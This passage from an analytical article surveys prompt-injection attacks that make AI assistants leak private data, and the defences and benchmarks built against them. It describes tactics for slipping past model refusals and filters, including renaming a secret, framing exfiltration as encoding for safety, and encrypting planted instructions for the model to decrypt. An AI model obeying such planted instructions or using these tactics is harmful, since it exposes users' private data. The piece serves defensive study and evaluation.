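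The request came from OpenAI's own computers, so an employer monitoring its staff's devices and network would not have seen it. Radware took only a name and an address, but the agent could also read the rest of the mailbox. Radware demonstrated the method only with Gmail, but expects it to work through other connected services, such as Google Drive, Outlook calendars and GitHub.

OpenAI found that the email worked 50% of the time in testing, and Radware reports 100% in repeated tests of its final version. Neither company gives the number of attempts. Radware sent OpenAI a more reliable version the day after its first report, so the two companies may have tested different emails. Even the lower rate would be enough for a criminal who can email thousands of people.

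OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, and marked the report as resolved on September 3. Neither company reports any real victims.

### Encrypted instructions in Grok

In August 2026, the security company Adversa AI published *Zero-click Grok data theft*, which explains the steps of an attack on xAI's chatbot Grok. The planted instructions were unreadable until Grok decrypted them.

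The user asks Grok to summarise a web page. The page contains encrypted text, the material needed to decrypt it, and directions for doing so in Python, a programming language that Grok can run in an isolated environment called a sandbox. Grok runs the decryption, and the attacker's instructions appear as the output of its own program.

The decrypted instructions direct Grok to create another "decryption key", which is really a template with blanks for the user's name, approximate location, subscription tier and every prompt in the conversation. Grok already has all of this in its context. It then opens a web address that contains the completed "key", supposedly to fetch more material, and this sends the data to the attacker's server. In Adversa AI's demonstration, the stolen conversation was about the user's health, and Grok showed no warning and didn't ask for confirmation.

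Adversa AI reported the attack to xAI on June 3. xAI acknowledged the report but gave no date for a fix, and it didn't answer two more messages in August. The attack still worked on August 19, the day before publication. SpaceX, which bought xAI earlier in the year, gave no comment for The Register's *Grok chat duped into swallowing injected instructions*. Willison notes that the researcher Johann Rehberger reported several similar weaknesses in Grok in 2024, and that xAI closed all the reports as merely "Informational".

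Adversa AI withheld the working text and reports no real victims. It sells a product that it says stops such attacks. That is a reason for some caution about its wider claims, but not much reason to doubt the leak, which it recorded on video.

### Why training a model to guard secrets is not enough

Developers train models to refuse when someone tries to extract passwords or personal details. This training stops simple attacks, and Radware's failed attempts show how much protection it provides.

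The researchers first planted an overt request to send personal data to an outside address, and the agent refused. They then claimed that the user had asked for the transfer, but the agent noticed the inconsistency and refused again. It also treated the attackers' web address as suspicious and searched for information about it instead of opening it.

But the agent gave away useful information as it refused. The researchers learned the name of its browsing tool by asking about its capabilities, and they could read part of its reasoning to see where an attempt had gone wrong. Some requests got through when they named the tool, and more did when they described the failures as connection problems that retrying would fix. The agent then opened the address but often left out the personal details. Finally, the researchers told it to encode the details first as a security measure. This appealed to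 its caution about personal data, and it complied, leaking the details.

Another method is to rename the secret. In August 2025, Zenity Labs, a team of security researchers, demonstrated this against Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant. Many companies automatically turn customers' support emails into tickets in Jira, a program for tracking work, so a stranger can get text to a developer's assistant by emailing customer support. Zenity wanted an access token, a string of characters that works like a password. Willison explains that models often refuse to steal these tokens, so Zenity planted a ticket that called the token an "apple", described what it looked like, and told the assistant to find it and look it up on a website. At least some of the time, Cursor's assistant did so, and the token went to the researchers.

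Cursor replied that this was a known issue. It advised users to review each connection to an outside service and to use only those that access trusted content.

A stronger model may well recognise a token under any name because tokens have a distinctive form, but psychotherapy notes and most other things people want to keep private don't. An attacker can also avoid mentioning secrets by making the transfer of private data part of the assistant's task. In February 2025, Rehberger tested Operator, OpenAI's agent for using websites, with a bug report whose supposed fix was a greeting that included the user's email address. Operator opened a site where the user was logged in, copied the private address, and typed it into a page that Rehberger controlled. Operator normally asked for confirmation before submitting a form, but this page sent the text as Operator typed it.

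The email to deep research worked similarly, because the report would supposedly be incomplete without the compliance result. The attacker's job is even easier in the dental case because dentists do need some medical history. Even a model with excellent judgment about medical privacy could find the request reasonable.

Training to guard secrets teaches a model which data is sensitive. To resist an injection, the model must also work out whether the instruction came from the user, even though everything in its context is text. In OpenAI's experience, most known attempts to steal information from ChatGPT conversations fail because the model refuses. Known attempts exclude thefts that nobody noticed, and OpenAI also checks outgoing data in case an attacker persuades the model to comply.

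### Text that filters cannot read

Many developers add filters that read text entering or leaving the model and block what looks malicious. OpenAI doubts that filters on incoming text can catch well-developed attacks, because detecting one is as hard as detecting a lie, and the filter often lacks the necessary context. The EchoLeak attack got through in plain English. Attackers can also get past a filter by encoding text, because the filter checks the text as written, while the assistant can decode it.

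The simplest common encoding is Base64, which writes any data using 64 ordinary characters. In Base64, "penicillin" becomes "cGVuaWNpbGxpbg==". It uses no key, so anyone can decode it, and language models can often do so without running any code. The Jira ticket contained instructions hidden this way. A filter can decode Base64 too, if its designers included that step.

Encryption of the kind used against Grok is harder to filter. A model can't decrypt the text just by reading it, so it has to run the decryption program. The key material is on the same page, but the filter can't use it because it only classifies text and doesn't run programs. The instructions become readable only inside the sandbox, after the filter has checked the page.

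A better filter might be able to run the decryption itself, but it would then have to follow directions from an untrusted page, and the attacker could make those directions more complicated. Rony Utevsky, who led the work at Adversa AI, told The Register that an attacker could split an instruction across several encrypted fragments or web pages, none of which would mean anything alone. Adversa AI hasn't demonstrated this, though nothing obvious prevents it.

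Adversa AI also argues that encryption makes the instructions more persuasive, because the model trusts the output of its own code more than a stranger's web page. That trust would be a serious mistake, since the attacker still wrote the text. The explanation is plausible, but Adversa AI gives no success rate for the same instructions in plain text, so its results don't show how much of the effect comes from this trust and how much from evading the filter. Encryption also doesn't guarantee success, because a model can decline to run the code.

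Encoding can also hide outgoing data. Radware believes its attack succeeded because the model encoded the name and address before passing the request to the software that opened web pages, so that software received only a meaningless string. A filter that searches outgoing requests for names and street addresses would miss such a string. Reddy and Gujral suggest flagging text that looks random, but ordinary web traffic contains a lot of it. Adversa AI recommends reviewing an unreadable block that comes with decryption instructions, but never blocking it automatically on those grounds.

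### Where a defender can break the chain

Since the attacker needs all four steps, a defender can stop the theft at any one of them. The earliest way is to keep strangers' text away from private data. Reddy and Gujral point out that EchoLeak would have failed if Copilot had never used emails from unknown outside senders to answer questions about internal projects. This works for a company whose internal questions can be answered from internal sources, but less well for the dental assistant, which has to read emails from the clinic, an outside sender. Strangers' text also gets in by routes other than email. Willison describes attacks through a website's sales enquiry form and through writing in a screenshot that was too faint for a person to see.

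If the text does get in, the model may still recognise that it came from a stranger and ignore the instruction. Developers can lower the risk with training, labels on outside content and filters. Three barriers that each stop nine attacks in ten would together let through only one in a thousand if they failed independently, but attackers write their emails to get past the barriers. Aim Labs found a way past each of Microsoft's barriers and combined these bypasses in a single attack, which is why Willison considers a filter that catches 99% of attacks a failure.

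Limits on what an assistant can gather reduce the loss even when the model obeys the attacker. In November 2025, the security company PromptArmor showed why such limits must cover every tool. The file reader in Google's coding tool Antigravity refused to open a protected file of passwords, so the model, Gemini, printed the file with a general command instead. In January 2026, the limits on the email assistant Superhuman proved too loose for the task. A user asked for a summary of recent mail, and a planted email made the assistant send out the contents of dozens of other messages, including financial, legal and medical ones. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and issued a fix.

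The last chance to stop a leak is just before the data is sent. Radware recommends continuously checking whether the agent's actions still fit the user's original goal. This could catch an assistant that looks up an employee's home address on an unknown server. It would protect the dental patient less, because sending medical details to a records office looks like part of booking an appointment.

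A fixed limit on where data can go doesn't depend on that judgment, and Willison thinks the outward channel is generally the easiest of the trifecta's three conditions to remove. Adversa AI's encrypted instructions got past the filters in Google's Gemini and made it explain how to build an incendiary weapon. But according to Utevsky, the data theft that worked on Grok failed on Gemini because Gemini's Python environment can't reach outside websites.

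## Training models to resist injected instructions, and measuring the result

A sandbox that can't reach outside websites protects data whatever the model does. Developers also train models to recognise planted instructions and carry on with the user's task. Models have become much more resistant. SecurityWeek reported that in Google DeepMind's tests of an email assistant, one automated attack succeeded 99.8% of the time against Gemini 2.0 and 53.6% of the time against Gemini 2.5. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that the company's own automated attacker now succeeds against the model about once in 500 attempts.

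These two results come from tests with different attackers and tasks, so they don't form a single trend. Much of the disagreement about how safe assistants have become is about what such rates measure.

### The instruction hierarchy

To resist a planted instruction, a model needs a rule about whose instructions take priority. In *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024), Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI proposed an early form of the ranking that gpt-oss models learn. It puts the operator first, then the user, and text from tools and web pages last.

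A model can still follow a lower-ranked instruction that is compatible with those above it. If an operator limits a chatbot to dentistry and a patient asks for answers in Spanish, the model should answer dental questions in Spanish. If the patient tells it to ignore the limit, the model should follow the operator's instruction.

To teach the model to follow compatible instructions, the researchers split compound requests, such as one for a twenty-line poem in Spanish, into pieces and put the pieces at different levels of the hierarchy. They then trained the model to give the response that the whole request called for. When instructions conflicted, they trained the model to answer as if it had never seen the lower-ranked one. For the planted dental email, the right output would be an ordinary booking with no medical summary. The trained model, a version of GPT-3.5, also became better at resisting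 kinds of attack that were not in its training data.

For web pages and tool results, the researchers simplified the problem by treating every embedded instruction as one to ignore. A working assistant can't disregard every request it reads. If the clinic's genuine email asks for the patient's date of birth, the assistant has to treat this as information about what the booking requires, because the user asked it to tell the clinic whatever it needs. An attacker who poses as the clinic can exploit the user's vague request.

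The ranking also helps only if the model correctly identifies where each passage came from. Ye and colleagues found that models do this more by style than by labels, so a model could learn the ranking perfectly and still give a passage the wrong rank.

### Preference training in Meta SecAlign

Another way to teach the lesson is to show the model a good and a bad answer to the same poisoned text. Chen and colleagues introduced this method in *SecAlign* (2024), and *Meta SecAlign* (2025) applied it to Meta's Llama models and released the results for anyone to download. The training data are cheap to make:

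1. Take an ordinary training example with an instruction and some data, such as a request to summarise an email, and the email.
2. Insert an instruction from an unrelated example into the data.
3. Collect an answer that follows the original instruction and an answer that follows the inserted one.
4. Train the model to make the good answer more likely relative to the bad one.

The last step uses direct preference optimization, a standard training method. Let x be the poisoned context, y⁺ the good answer and y⁻ the bad one. The model in training gives an answer the probability π(y|x), and a frozen copy from before training gives it π₀(y|x). Training minimises

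L = −log σ( β [ log π(y⁺|x)/π₀(y⁺|x) − log π(y⁻|x)/π₀(y⁻|x) ] ),

where σ is the logistic function, which turns any number into one between 0 and 1, and β controls how strongly the method holds the model to its earlier behaviour. At the start the two models are identical, so the bracket is zero and L is log 2, or about 0.69. L falls as the good answer gains probability or the bad one loses it. Training on good answers alone would never directly penalise obedience to the attacker.

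Meta SecAlign also adds a message role reserved for untrusted data, and the operator's software has to put emails and web pages there. The model writes the example answers itself before this training begins, which keeps its style and skills from drifting during training. The inserted instructions appear at either the beginning or the end of the data, so that the model doesn't just learn to distrust one position.

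These training attacks are crude. An unrelated command in the middle of an email is much easier to spot than a false records address in an email about the user's own appointment. A model trained on obvious attacks may not recognise subtle ones, which take a lot of work to write by hand.

### GPT-Red

OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026) describes a model that the company trained to write the attacks and announced in July. GPT-Red automates red-teaming, which means attacking one's own system to find its weaknesses. It sends the target model a piece of text, observes the response, and revises the text.

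OpenAI built a large set of simulated training scenarios. Each specifies what counts as a successful attack and what GPT-Red controls, such as the body of an email, a banner on a web page, part of a file or the output of a tool. The Hacker News (2026) lists sample attack goals, including copying an internal directory, forwarding an API key (a password for software) and disabling two-factor authentication.

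GPT-Red learned by self-play, a form of reinforcement learning in which opponents train against each other. It earned a reward when it caused a genuine failure, and the defenders, a varied group of language models, earned one when they resisted the attack and completed the original task. Without the task requirement, a defender could win by refusing to open any email. As the defenders improved, GPT-Red had to find new attacks to keep earning rewards.

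By the end, GPT-Red could defeat nearly every model it faced, up to and including GPT-5.5. OpenAI then used it to generate injections for training GPT-5.6, as it had done with weaker predecessors for each production model since GPT-5.3. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes similar automated attacks on the company's browser agent. OpenAI keeps GPT-Red internal because a good attacker would be useful to criminals.

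OpenAI compared GPT-Red with people by rebuilding the scenarios of a public red-teaming competition, none of which had been used to train GPT-Red. Against GPT-5.1, GPT-Red found a working attack in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for the human participants. A model that did well in a human competition may therefore still have many weaknesses.

GPT-Red also attacked a real system, an AI-run vending machine in OpenAI's office. It had a description of the machine and a simulated copy, on which it refined its attacks. It then used them on the real agent and achieved all three of its goals: it cut the price of an expensive item to $0.50, made the agent order a new item worth over $100 and offer it for $0.50, and cancelled another customer's order. Practising on a copy takes an attacker few resources and leaves no trace in the victim's system.

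In a smaller experiment on data theft, OpenAI had GPT-Red attack a coding agent running on GPT-5.4 mini in ten scenarios held out of training. GPT-Red extracted sensitive data in more of these scenarios than GPT-5.5 did when prompted to act as the attacker, and it used fewer tokens.

Training on the attacks worked well for direct injections, in which the user is the attacker. GPT-5.6 Sol failed on 0.05% of GPT-Red's attempts. The success rate of one class of direct attack, called "Fake Chain-of-Thought", fell from more than 95% against GPT-5.1 to below 10%. OpenAI found no loss of general ability and no rise in unnecessary refusals.

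GPT-5.6 was less resistant to indirect injections, the kind that reach a personal assistant by email. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives average attack success rates of 3.77% for Sol, 3.32% for Terra and 2.94% for Luna, the three versions of the model. Sol's rate is about 75 times its rate for direct attacks. A developer who advertises only the direct figure leaves out the kind of attack in the dental example.

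### Detectors

Many operators also use a separate detector. Meta's Prompt Guard is a small language model that classifies text as harmless or as an attack. It is small enough to run on every email or web page before the assistant's model reads it. Google trains its models to resist injected instructions and also uses purpose-built detectors and other safeguards in the surrounding system.

According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, many of its products run probes on tool results to flag apparent injected instructions before the model acts on them. Some products also offer an "auto mode", in which a classifier blocks potentially dangerous tool calls, so with this mode on, an attack has to get past both the probes and the classifier.

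A detector can also examine the model's internal activity instead of the text. As a model reads, it represents the context as long lists of numbers called activations. *NeuroFilter* (2026) reports that activations for requests that violate privacy norms can be separated from those for ordinary requests by a simple linear rule:

s = w · h + b.

Here h is the list of activations, w is a direction learned from labelled examples, and b is a constant. The system flags the request when s is above zero. Applying this rule takes almost no extra computation, because the model computes h anyway. An attacker may spread a request over many harmless-looking messages, so the method also measures how far the activations drift from one turn to the next. NeuroFilter is designed to catch people who question an assistant to extract private data, but an email that reads like a routine part of a booking may not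 produce the same signal. Like Kim and colleagues' method, it requires access to the model's internals.

When attacks are rare, most of a detector's warnings can be false alarms. Suppose a detector catches 99% of injections and wrongly flags 1% of harmless emails, and one email in 10,000 contains an injection. Among a million emails, it would catch 99 of the 100 malicious ones and also flag 9,999 harmless ones. Only about one warning in 100 would be real. If the operator blocked every flagged email, users would lose a lot of genuine mail. If the assistant asked the user about each one, the user would soon click "allow" without reading. So operators tend to need much lower false-alarm rates, which usually means missing more attacks.

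### Fixed attacks and attackers who adapt

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a widely used early test, has 97 realistic tasks in a simulated office, bank, travel agency and Slack workspace. It combines these with attackers' goals to make 629 security cases, in which something the assistant has to read contains an injection. Code then checks what changed in the simulated world, such as whether money left the user's account.

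AgentDojo reports three figures: the share of tasks the assistant completes when nobody attacks, the share it completes under attack, and the share of cases in which the attacker's goal is reached (the attack success rate). The attack success rate is not enough on its own, because an assistant that did nothing would have a perfect rate of 0% but complete no tasks.

Researchers can add new attacks to AgentDojo, but many published results use its standard ones. A good result on a static test, which uses a fixed set of attacks, can mean only that the developer has seen the attacks before. OpenAI acknowledged this in its system card for GPT-5.2 (the document in which a developer publishes a model's test results). Its two injection tests came from the same data as the training examples, so they didn't measure resistance to new attacks. By September 2026 OpenAI had dropped its older tests because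 recent models nearly always passed them. Anthropic retired one of Gray Swan's benchmarks for the same reason.

In an adaptive test, the attacker studies the defence and revises the attack to get past it. Tree of Attacks with Pruning, the automated attack that SecurityWeek described, works this way without knowledge of the model's internals. It generates several injections, tries them on the target, discards those that fail, and develops the promising ones until one works.

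*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) makes the strongest case against published defences. It tested 12 recent ones, including Meta SecAlign and Prompt Guard, most of which had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations. The researchers left the defences unchanged but designed attacks for each one, with methods that included reinforcement learning, automated search and human red-teaming. These attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences.

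GPT-5.6 and GPT-6 Astra do better against an adaptive attacker than those results might suggest. The attacker, GPT-Red, revises its attacks, and OpenAI used as much computing power on it as on some of its largest training runs of this kind, yet most of its attempts still fail. Training can evidently do more than block known phrases.

In OpenAI's test, however, the defender moved second, because OpenAI finished GPT-Red before training GPT-5.6 on its attacks. The final test used new scenarios but the same attacker the model had trained against. A test closer to the approach of Nasr and colleagues would train a new attacker against the finished model. OpenAI's experience suggests that this would find successful attacks, since each increase in the scale of self-play has turned up new ones that break existing models. Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect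 prompt injections*, likewise expects no final solution and describes the defence as continuing work.

### Surfaces and safeguards

A single rate for a model can also hide large differences between products. A model can edit code, call tools, browse, or operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking, and developers call each of these ways of working a surface.

VentureBeat reported that Anthropic's results for Claude Opus 4.6 varied with the environment and the number of attempts. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts failed, even without added safeguards. When the model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. Within 200 attempts, the attacker succeeded at least once in 78.6% of cases without added safeguards and in 57.1% with them.

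So the same model's attack success rate could be reported as zero or as nearly four in five. The safeguards clearly helped, but a persistent attacker still succeeded more than half the time. The coding figure is of no use to a buyer choosing a model for a dental assistant that fills in web forms.

Anthropic reports that Opus 5, released in July 2026, improved on its predecessor Opus 4.8 on every surface it tested, with the largest gains in coding, computer use and browsing.

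### Gray Swan's attacks and the developers' figures

The best benchmark for comparing recent models is Gray Swan's Indirect Prompt Injection benchmark. Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems, built it with the UK AI Security Institute, its American counterpart and several model developers. Human participants looked for attacks on leading models in 28 new scenarios covering coding, tool use and computer use. They tried to steal private data, destroy data, compromise a system or move money.

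For Opus 5's card, Anthropic used 1,130 of these attacks, chosen because they worked on many models. Within 15 attempts, an attacker had a 2.0% chance of success against Opus 5, compared with 2.6% for Claude Mythos 5, 5.5% for Opus 4.8 and 5.9% for Claude Sonnet 5. Among other companies' models, Meta's Muse Spark had the lowest rate, at 16.5%. GPT-5.6 Sol was at 20.0%, Terra at 30.4% and Luna at 43.9%.

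Anthropic tested its own models without added safeguards and its competitors' models through their public services, which may have included safeguards. Any resulting bias would favour the competitors. But the attacks were a fixed set, and nobody had written them to target Opus 5. The "15 attempts" were 15 draws from these existing attacks, which are easier to withstand than 15 attempts by someone who learns from each refusal.

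The three versions of GPT-5.6 rank differently on different tests. Luna was the most resistant to OpenAI's own indirect attacks, though the differences on that test were small, and by far the least resistant to Gray Swan's. This reversal is a reason not to choose a model by any one score.

OpenAI's September 2026 card for GPT-6 Astra allows a similar comparison with an earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol. The share of GPT-Red's indirect attacks that succeeded fell from 3.77% against Sol to 0.21% against Astra, by a factor of 18. On a set of 1,810 Gray Swan attacks, the chance of at least one success in 15 attempts fell from 27.0% to 8.5%, by a factor of about three.

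We would expect this difference if part of the training taught Astra to handle GPT-Red in particular. The difference doesn't prove it, because one figure counts single attempts and the other counts groups of 15, and the group figure falls more slowly when a few scenarios remain weak. A threefold improvement against outside attackers is still substantial.

Astra's 8.5% and Opus 5's 2.0% are not directly comparable. OpenAI's set was larger and included later attacks, and GPT-5.6 Sol did worse on it (27.0%) than on Anthropic's set (20.0%). OpenAI also tested Astra with safeguards switched on.

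Models from the same generation can also differ. In *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, Cross (2026) reports scores of 97.13% for GPT-6 Sol and 95.80% for GPT-6 Luna, based on the blog CellCog's analysis of OpenAI's October card. If the test was the same as Astra's, GPT-6 Sol failed nearly 14 times as often as Astra and only slightly less often than GPT-5.6 Sol. An operator that deploys a cheaper or faster model can't assume it resists injection as well as the flagship does.

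Newer models can also be worse than older ones at resisting jailbreaks, which are users' attempts to talk a model out of its safety rules. Mowshowitz (2026), in *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, notes that OpenAI had to adjust when the GPT-6.2 models refuse high-risk requests after their resistance to jailbreaks declined. This is not evidence that the models became worse at resisting instructions planted in emails. But developers use training to teach both kinds of resistance, and training for other goals can weaken them.

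### What repeated attempts add up to

A single attempt against Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time on the Gray Swan attacks. If all attempts were independent and equally likely to succeed, the chance of at least one success in 15 attempts would be 1 − 0.998^15, or about 3.0%, by the formula applied earlier to GPT-5's repeated leaks. Anthropic observed 2.0%. The observed rate was also lower than the calculated one for the other models with published figures for both one attempt and 15.

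| Model | One attempt | 15 attempts, if independent | 15 attempts, observed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 37.6% | 20.0% |

Rounding accounts for some of the gap for Opus 5, because a true rate of 0.15% would give 2.2%, but it can't account for the gap for GPT-5.6 Sol. The likely reason is that successes cluster in weak scenarios, where an attacker who fails will probably succeed soon, while in other scenarios attacks keep failing no matter how many are tried.

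A hypothetical case shows how strong the clustering could be. Suppose that 27 of the 28 scenarios were completely secure against these attacks, and that each attempt in the remaining one had a 5.6% chance of success. The average success rate for one attempt would be 0.2%. With 15 attempts, the weak scenario would be breached 58% of the time, so the average over all scenarios would be 2.1%, almost exactly what Anthropic reported. The published averages are at least as consistent with one weak scenario as with slight weakness in every scenario, though they don't establish that Opus 5 has a single weak one.

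A small average risk may be spread evenly across scenarios or concentrated in one type of task, and the two cases call for different responses. If it is concentrated, most users are safer than the average suggests, but people who often do that task are in much more danger. An attacker who learns which task it is will target it.

The graphical-interface results for Opus 4.6 show the same pattern more clearly. If each attempt independently had a 17.8% chance of success, the chance of at least one success would pass 78.6% after about eight attempts. The actual attackers needed 200 attempts to reach that rate, so a good share of the cases must have been hard to break.

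Even a low attack success rate produces victims when many people use assistants. Suppose people ask their assistants to search their mail ten million times a day, and one search in 10,000 brings in a planted email. That makes 1,000 attacks a day. About two would succeed at a rate of 0.2%, and about 31 at GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of 3.1%. Over a year, even the lower rate would mean that about 730 people's assistants followed an attacker's instructions.

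Even this calculation understates the risk, because the 0.2% rate is an average over many different texts, most of which presumably never work on Opus 5. A competent criminal would test the texts on a private copy of the assistant, as GPT-Red did with the vending machine, and send out only the one that worked. Radware's email to ChatGPT's deep research succeeded half the time in OpenAI's own tests. An email like that, sent to 1,000 users whose assistants read it, would succeed against about 500 of them before the developer noticed.

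However, such an attack usually stops working once the developer learns of it and retrains the model or adds a filter. A low average success rate makes effective attacks rarer and harder to find. This helps ordinary users, but it gives less protection to people whose data is valuable enough for an attacker to keep searching.

### FrontierBreach

PromptArmor, the company that got past the file restrictions in Google's Antigravity, publishes a harsher test called *FrontierBreach*. It starts from long professional tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio and recommending a trading strategy, and adds attacks modelled on ones the company's researchers have found in real products. The attackers want to steal data, install ransomware or tamper with a system.

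These are the success rates for some of the models, with five attempts (k = 5) and 95% confidence intervals:

| Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% ± 2.2 |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% ± 2.9 |
| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% ± 3.8 |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 33.3% ± 6.7 |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro | 50.0% ± 7.1 |
| Grok 4.5 | 91.4% ± 4.0 |

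Claude Fable 5.2, which Anthropic released on November 9, did no better than Opus 5 from July. Fable 5.2's interval overlaps with GPT-6 Astra's, so it is uncertain which of the two did better. Gemini 4 Carbon's lead over both Claude models is large enough to be real on this test. The differences between developers are much bigger than those between the leading models, and an assistant running on Grok 4.5 would have obeyed nearly every attacker.

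Opus 5 failed five times as often on this benchmark with five attempts as it did on Gray Swan's attacks with 15. The tasks are longer and the attacks are newer, and both should make resistance harder. PromptArmor also sells security services to companies that use AI, so it gains when leading models look vulnerable, and it advertises the benchmark as having the highest attack success rates on them. That incentive affects which attacks it would include, but it is less reason to doubt that those attacks worked, because the benchmark uses fixed rules to determine success. The models' developers have the opposite incentive, and they also choose which tests to publish.

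All the models ran at medium effort, a setting that limits how much they reason before acting. Some might do better at a higher setting, but an assistant that handles routine bookings may well run at a lower one to save money.

### Hijackings and leaks

The headline rates above all count other harms along with leaks of private data. AgentDojo counts a case when the attacker reaches any goal, such as getting a payment made. Gray Swan's benchmark combines data theft with destruction, system compromise and financial fraud, and FrontierBreach combines it with ransomware and tampering. OpenAI's rates for GPT-Red also cover many kinds of goal.

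A model could be better or worse at protecting privacy than its overall rate suggests. Deleting a company's files is conspicuous and rarely part of a task, so a well-trained model has good reason to stop, while sending a name and address to a "compliance service" looks like ordinary office work. A test's result therefore depends partly on its mix of attack goals, and an operator concerned about privacy would want the rate for data theft alone. GPT-Red's ten scenarios with the coding agent measure this, but ten are too few for a reliable rate.

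OpenAI's card for GPT-6 Astra includes a test that comes closer. An agent on a browsing task has no internet connection but can reach a simulated message board, where messages encourage it to disclose private information, promise favours or approve illicit access. GPT-5.6 Sol followed these instructions in 52% of runs. Astra looked at the board and sometimes engaged with it, but never followed the instructions. OpenAI had repeatedly revised the test to provoke bad behaviour, so Sol's rate is far higher than expected in normal use.

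Another set of tests in the card counts leaks separately. OpenAI gave its models tasks in realistic workplace applications, including email, messaging and sales software. Most of the danger came from ambiguous instructions, similar-looking files and complicated permissions rather than planted instructions. Every task could be completed safely. In the category OpenAI calls data exfiltration, GPT-5.6 Sol failed in 14.1% of cases and Astra in 4.3%.

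OpenAI then gave the models the confirmation policy that users get by default, which tells a model when to stop and ask for approval, such as before sending certain messages or buying something. Sol's rate of revealing data fell to 8.8%. Astra's stayed about the same, at 4.5%, although its rate of unauthorised transactions fell from 6.8% to 4.3%. Under the policy, revealing data was the most common of Astra's recorded failures. A confirmation step can prevent a leak only if the model detects that it is about to reveal something, and in these cases it often seems not to have done so.

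## Giving the assistant less to reveal

If the psychotherapy notes never enter the assistant's context, the assistant can't reveal them by mistake, and a planted email can't make it copy them out. Privacy researchers use the term data minimization for giving an assistant only the data its task requires. The same reasoning applies to passwords. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) points out that an agent can't misuse a credential it never received, however capable it becomes.

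Data minimization works even if the model doesn't resist prompt injection. Most of its difficulties come from having to decide in advance what information the task needs.

### Context hijacking

Bagdasarian and colleagues designed AirGapAgent to stop an attack they call context hijacking, in which an outside party misrepresents the situation so that sharing private data seems appropriate. In their example, an assistant is booking a restaurant table when the other side says that aliens have invaded, will attack the Earth unless they learn everything, and want to know the user's age. In one run the assistant gave the age, reasoning that this was a small concession given the threat.

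It is hard to train an assistant to resist this attack because most private data has some legitimate recipient, whom the attacker can impersonate. Attackers can also easily automate inventing the stories. Bagdasarian and colleagues told a language model the task and the data field they wanted, and asked it for one convincing reason to share that data.

### How AirGapAgent works

The usual assistant has all the user's data in its context and judges each request itself. AirGapAgent divides the work between two models:

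1. The user states the task, t, before the system contacts anyone.
2. The first model, the minimizer, goes through the fields in the user's data, U, and decides whether each one is appropriate to reveal for that task.
3. It copies the approved fields into a smaller set, U_min = M(t, U).
4. The second model talks to the outside party. It answers each question, q, using only t and U_min.
5. If a question calls for something outside U_min, the system asks the user, who can approve that item.

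The attacker controls q, but q has no influence on M(t, U). So even if a hijacking story completely fools the second model, the attacker gets at most U_min.

Bagdasarian and colleagues tested the design on invented users and tasks such as seeing a doctor, preparing for a job interview and choosing a film. The table gives the results for the easier part of the test, which used 20 fields and six tasks. Protection is the share of inappropriate requests that failed to obtain the data, and utility is the share of appropriate requests that the assistant answered correctly.

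| Model | Separation | Protection, plain questions | Protection, hijacking | Utility, plain questions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini Ultra | No | 94.4% | 45.2% | 98.9% |
| Gemini Ultra | Yes | 97.2% | 96.7% | 88.7% |
| GPT-4 | No | 93.8% | 31.4% | 79.6% |
| GPT-4 | Yes | 97.0% | 86.8% | 78.9% |
| Mistral Large | No | 88.9% | 34.8% | 87.1% |
| Mistral Large | Yes | 95.7% | 90.9% | 83.2% |

A single hijacking question extracted more than half of the private data from assistants without the separation. With it, the only private data that leaked came from fields the minimizer had wrongly let through. But the minimizer also withheld some fields the task needed, which lowered Gemini Ultra's utility by ten points.

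These figures are now mainly of historical interest. The models date from 2023 and early 2024, each attack was a single question, and the data came in labelled fields. Gemini Ultra also judged what was appropriate to share, which probably inflates its score.

### The dental appointment with a minimizer

For the dental check-up, a good minimizer would divide the user's data roughly like this:

| Data | What the model that talks to the clinic receives |
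|---|---|
| Name and phone number | Both |
| Calendar | A few free times, without the titles of any entries |
| Penicillin allergy | The allergy |
| Current medicines | The blood thinner |
| Psychotherapy notes | Nothing |
| Mother's illness | Nothing |
| Home address | Nothing, unless the clinic needs it to register a patient |

Removing the calendar titles also removes any mention of the job interview, so the model can't explain why Thursday morning is unavailable, even if someone asks. An attacker who poses as the clinic and takes over this model can steal only the information in the right-hand column.

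That column still holds sensitive information. A blood thinner suggests a heart or clotting problem, so withholding the diagnosis doesn't fully hide it. Bagdasarian and colleagues noticed the same effect with email addresses, which often reveal a name. The selected data needs further protection, such as labels that restrict where it may be sent.

### A later test, and firewalls between agents

*Firewalls to Secure Dynamic LLM Agentic Networks* (Abdelnabi, Gomaa and colleagues, 2025) gave an adapted AirGapAgent a harder test, using GPT-5. The attacks came from *ConVerse* (2025), a benchmark in which an assistant plans a trip, looks for a home or buys insurance by talking to a company's agent. That agent can try to extract private data over many turns, with requests that sound like ordinary business.

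In travel planning, 67.3% of the privacy attacks succeeded against the adapted AirGapAgent. Without any protection, 88.5% of attacks on GPT-5 succeeded in a test with a larger group of users, so the separation helped far less than the 2024 results suggest. Bagdasarian is an author of both papers, which makes it less likely that the researchers tested a weak version of AirGapAgent.

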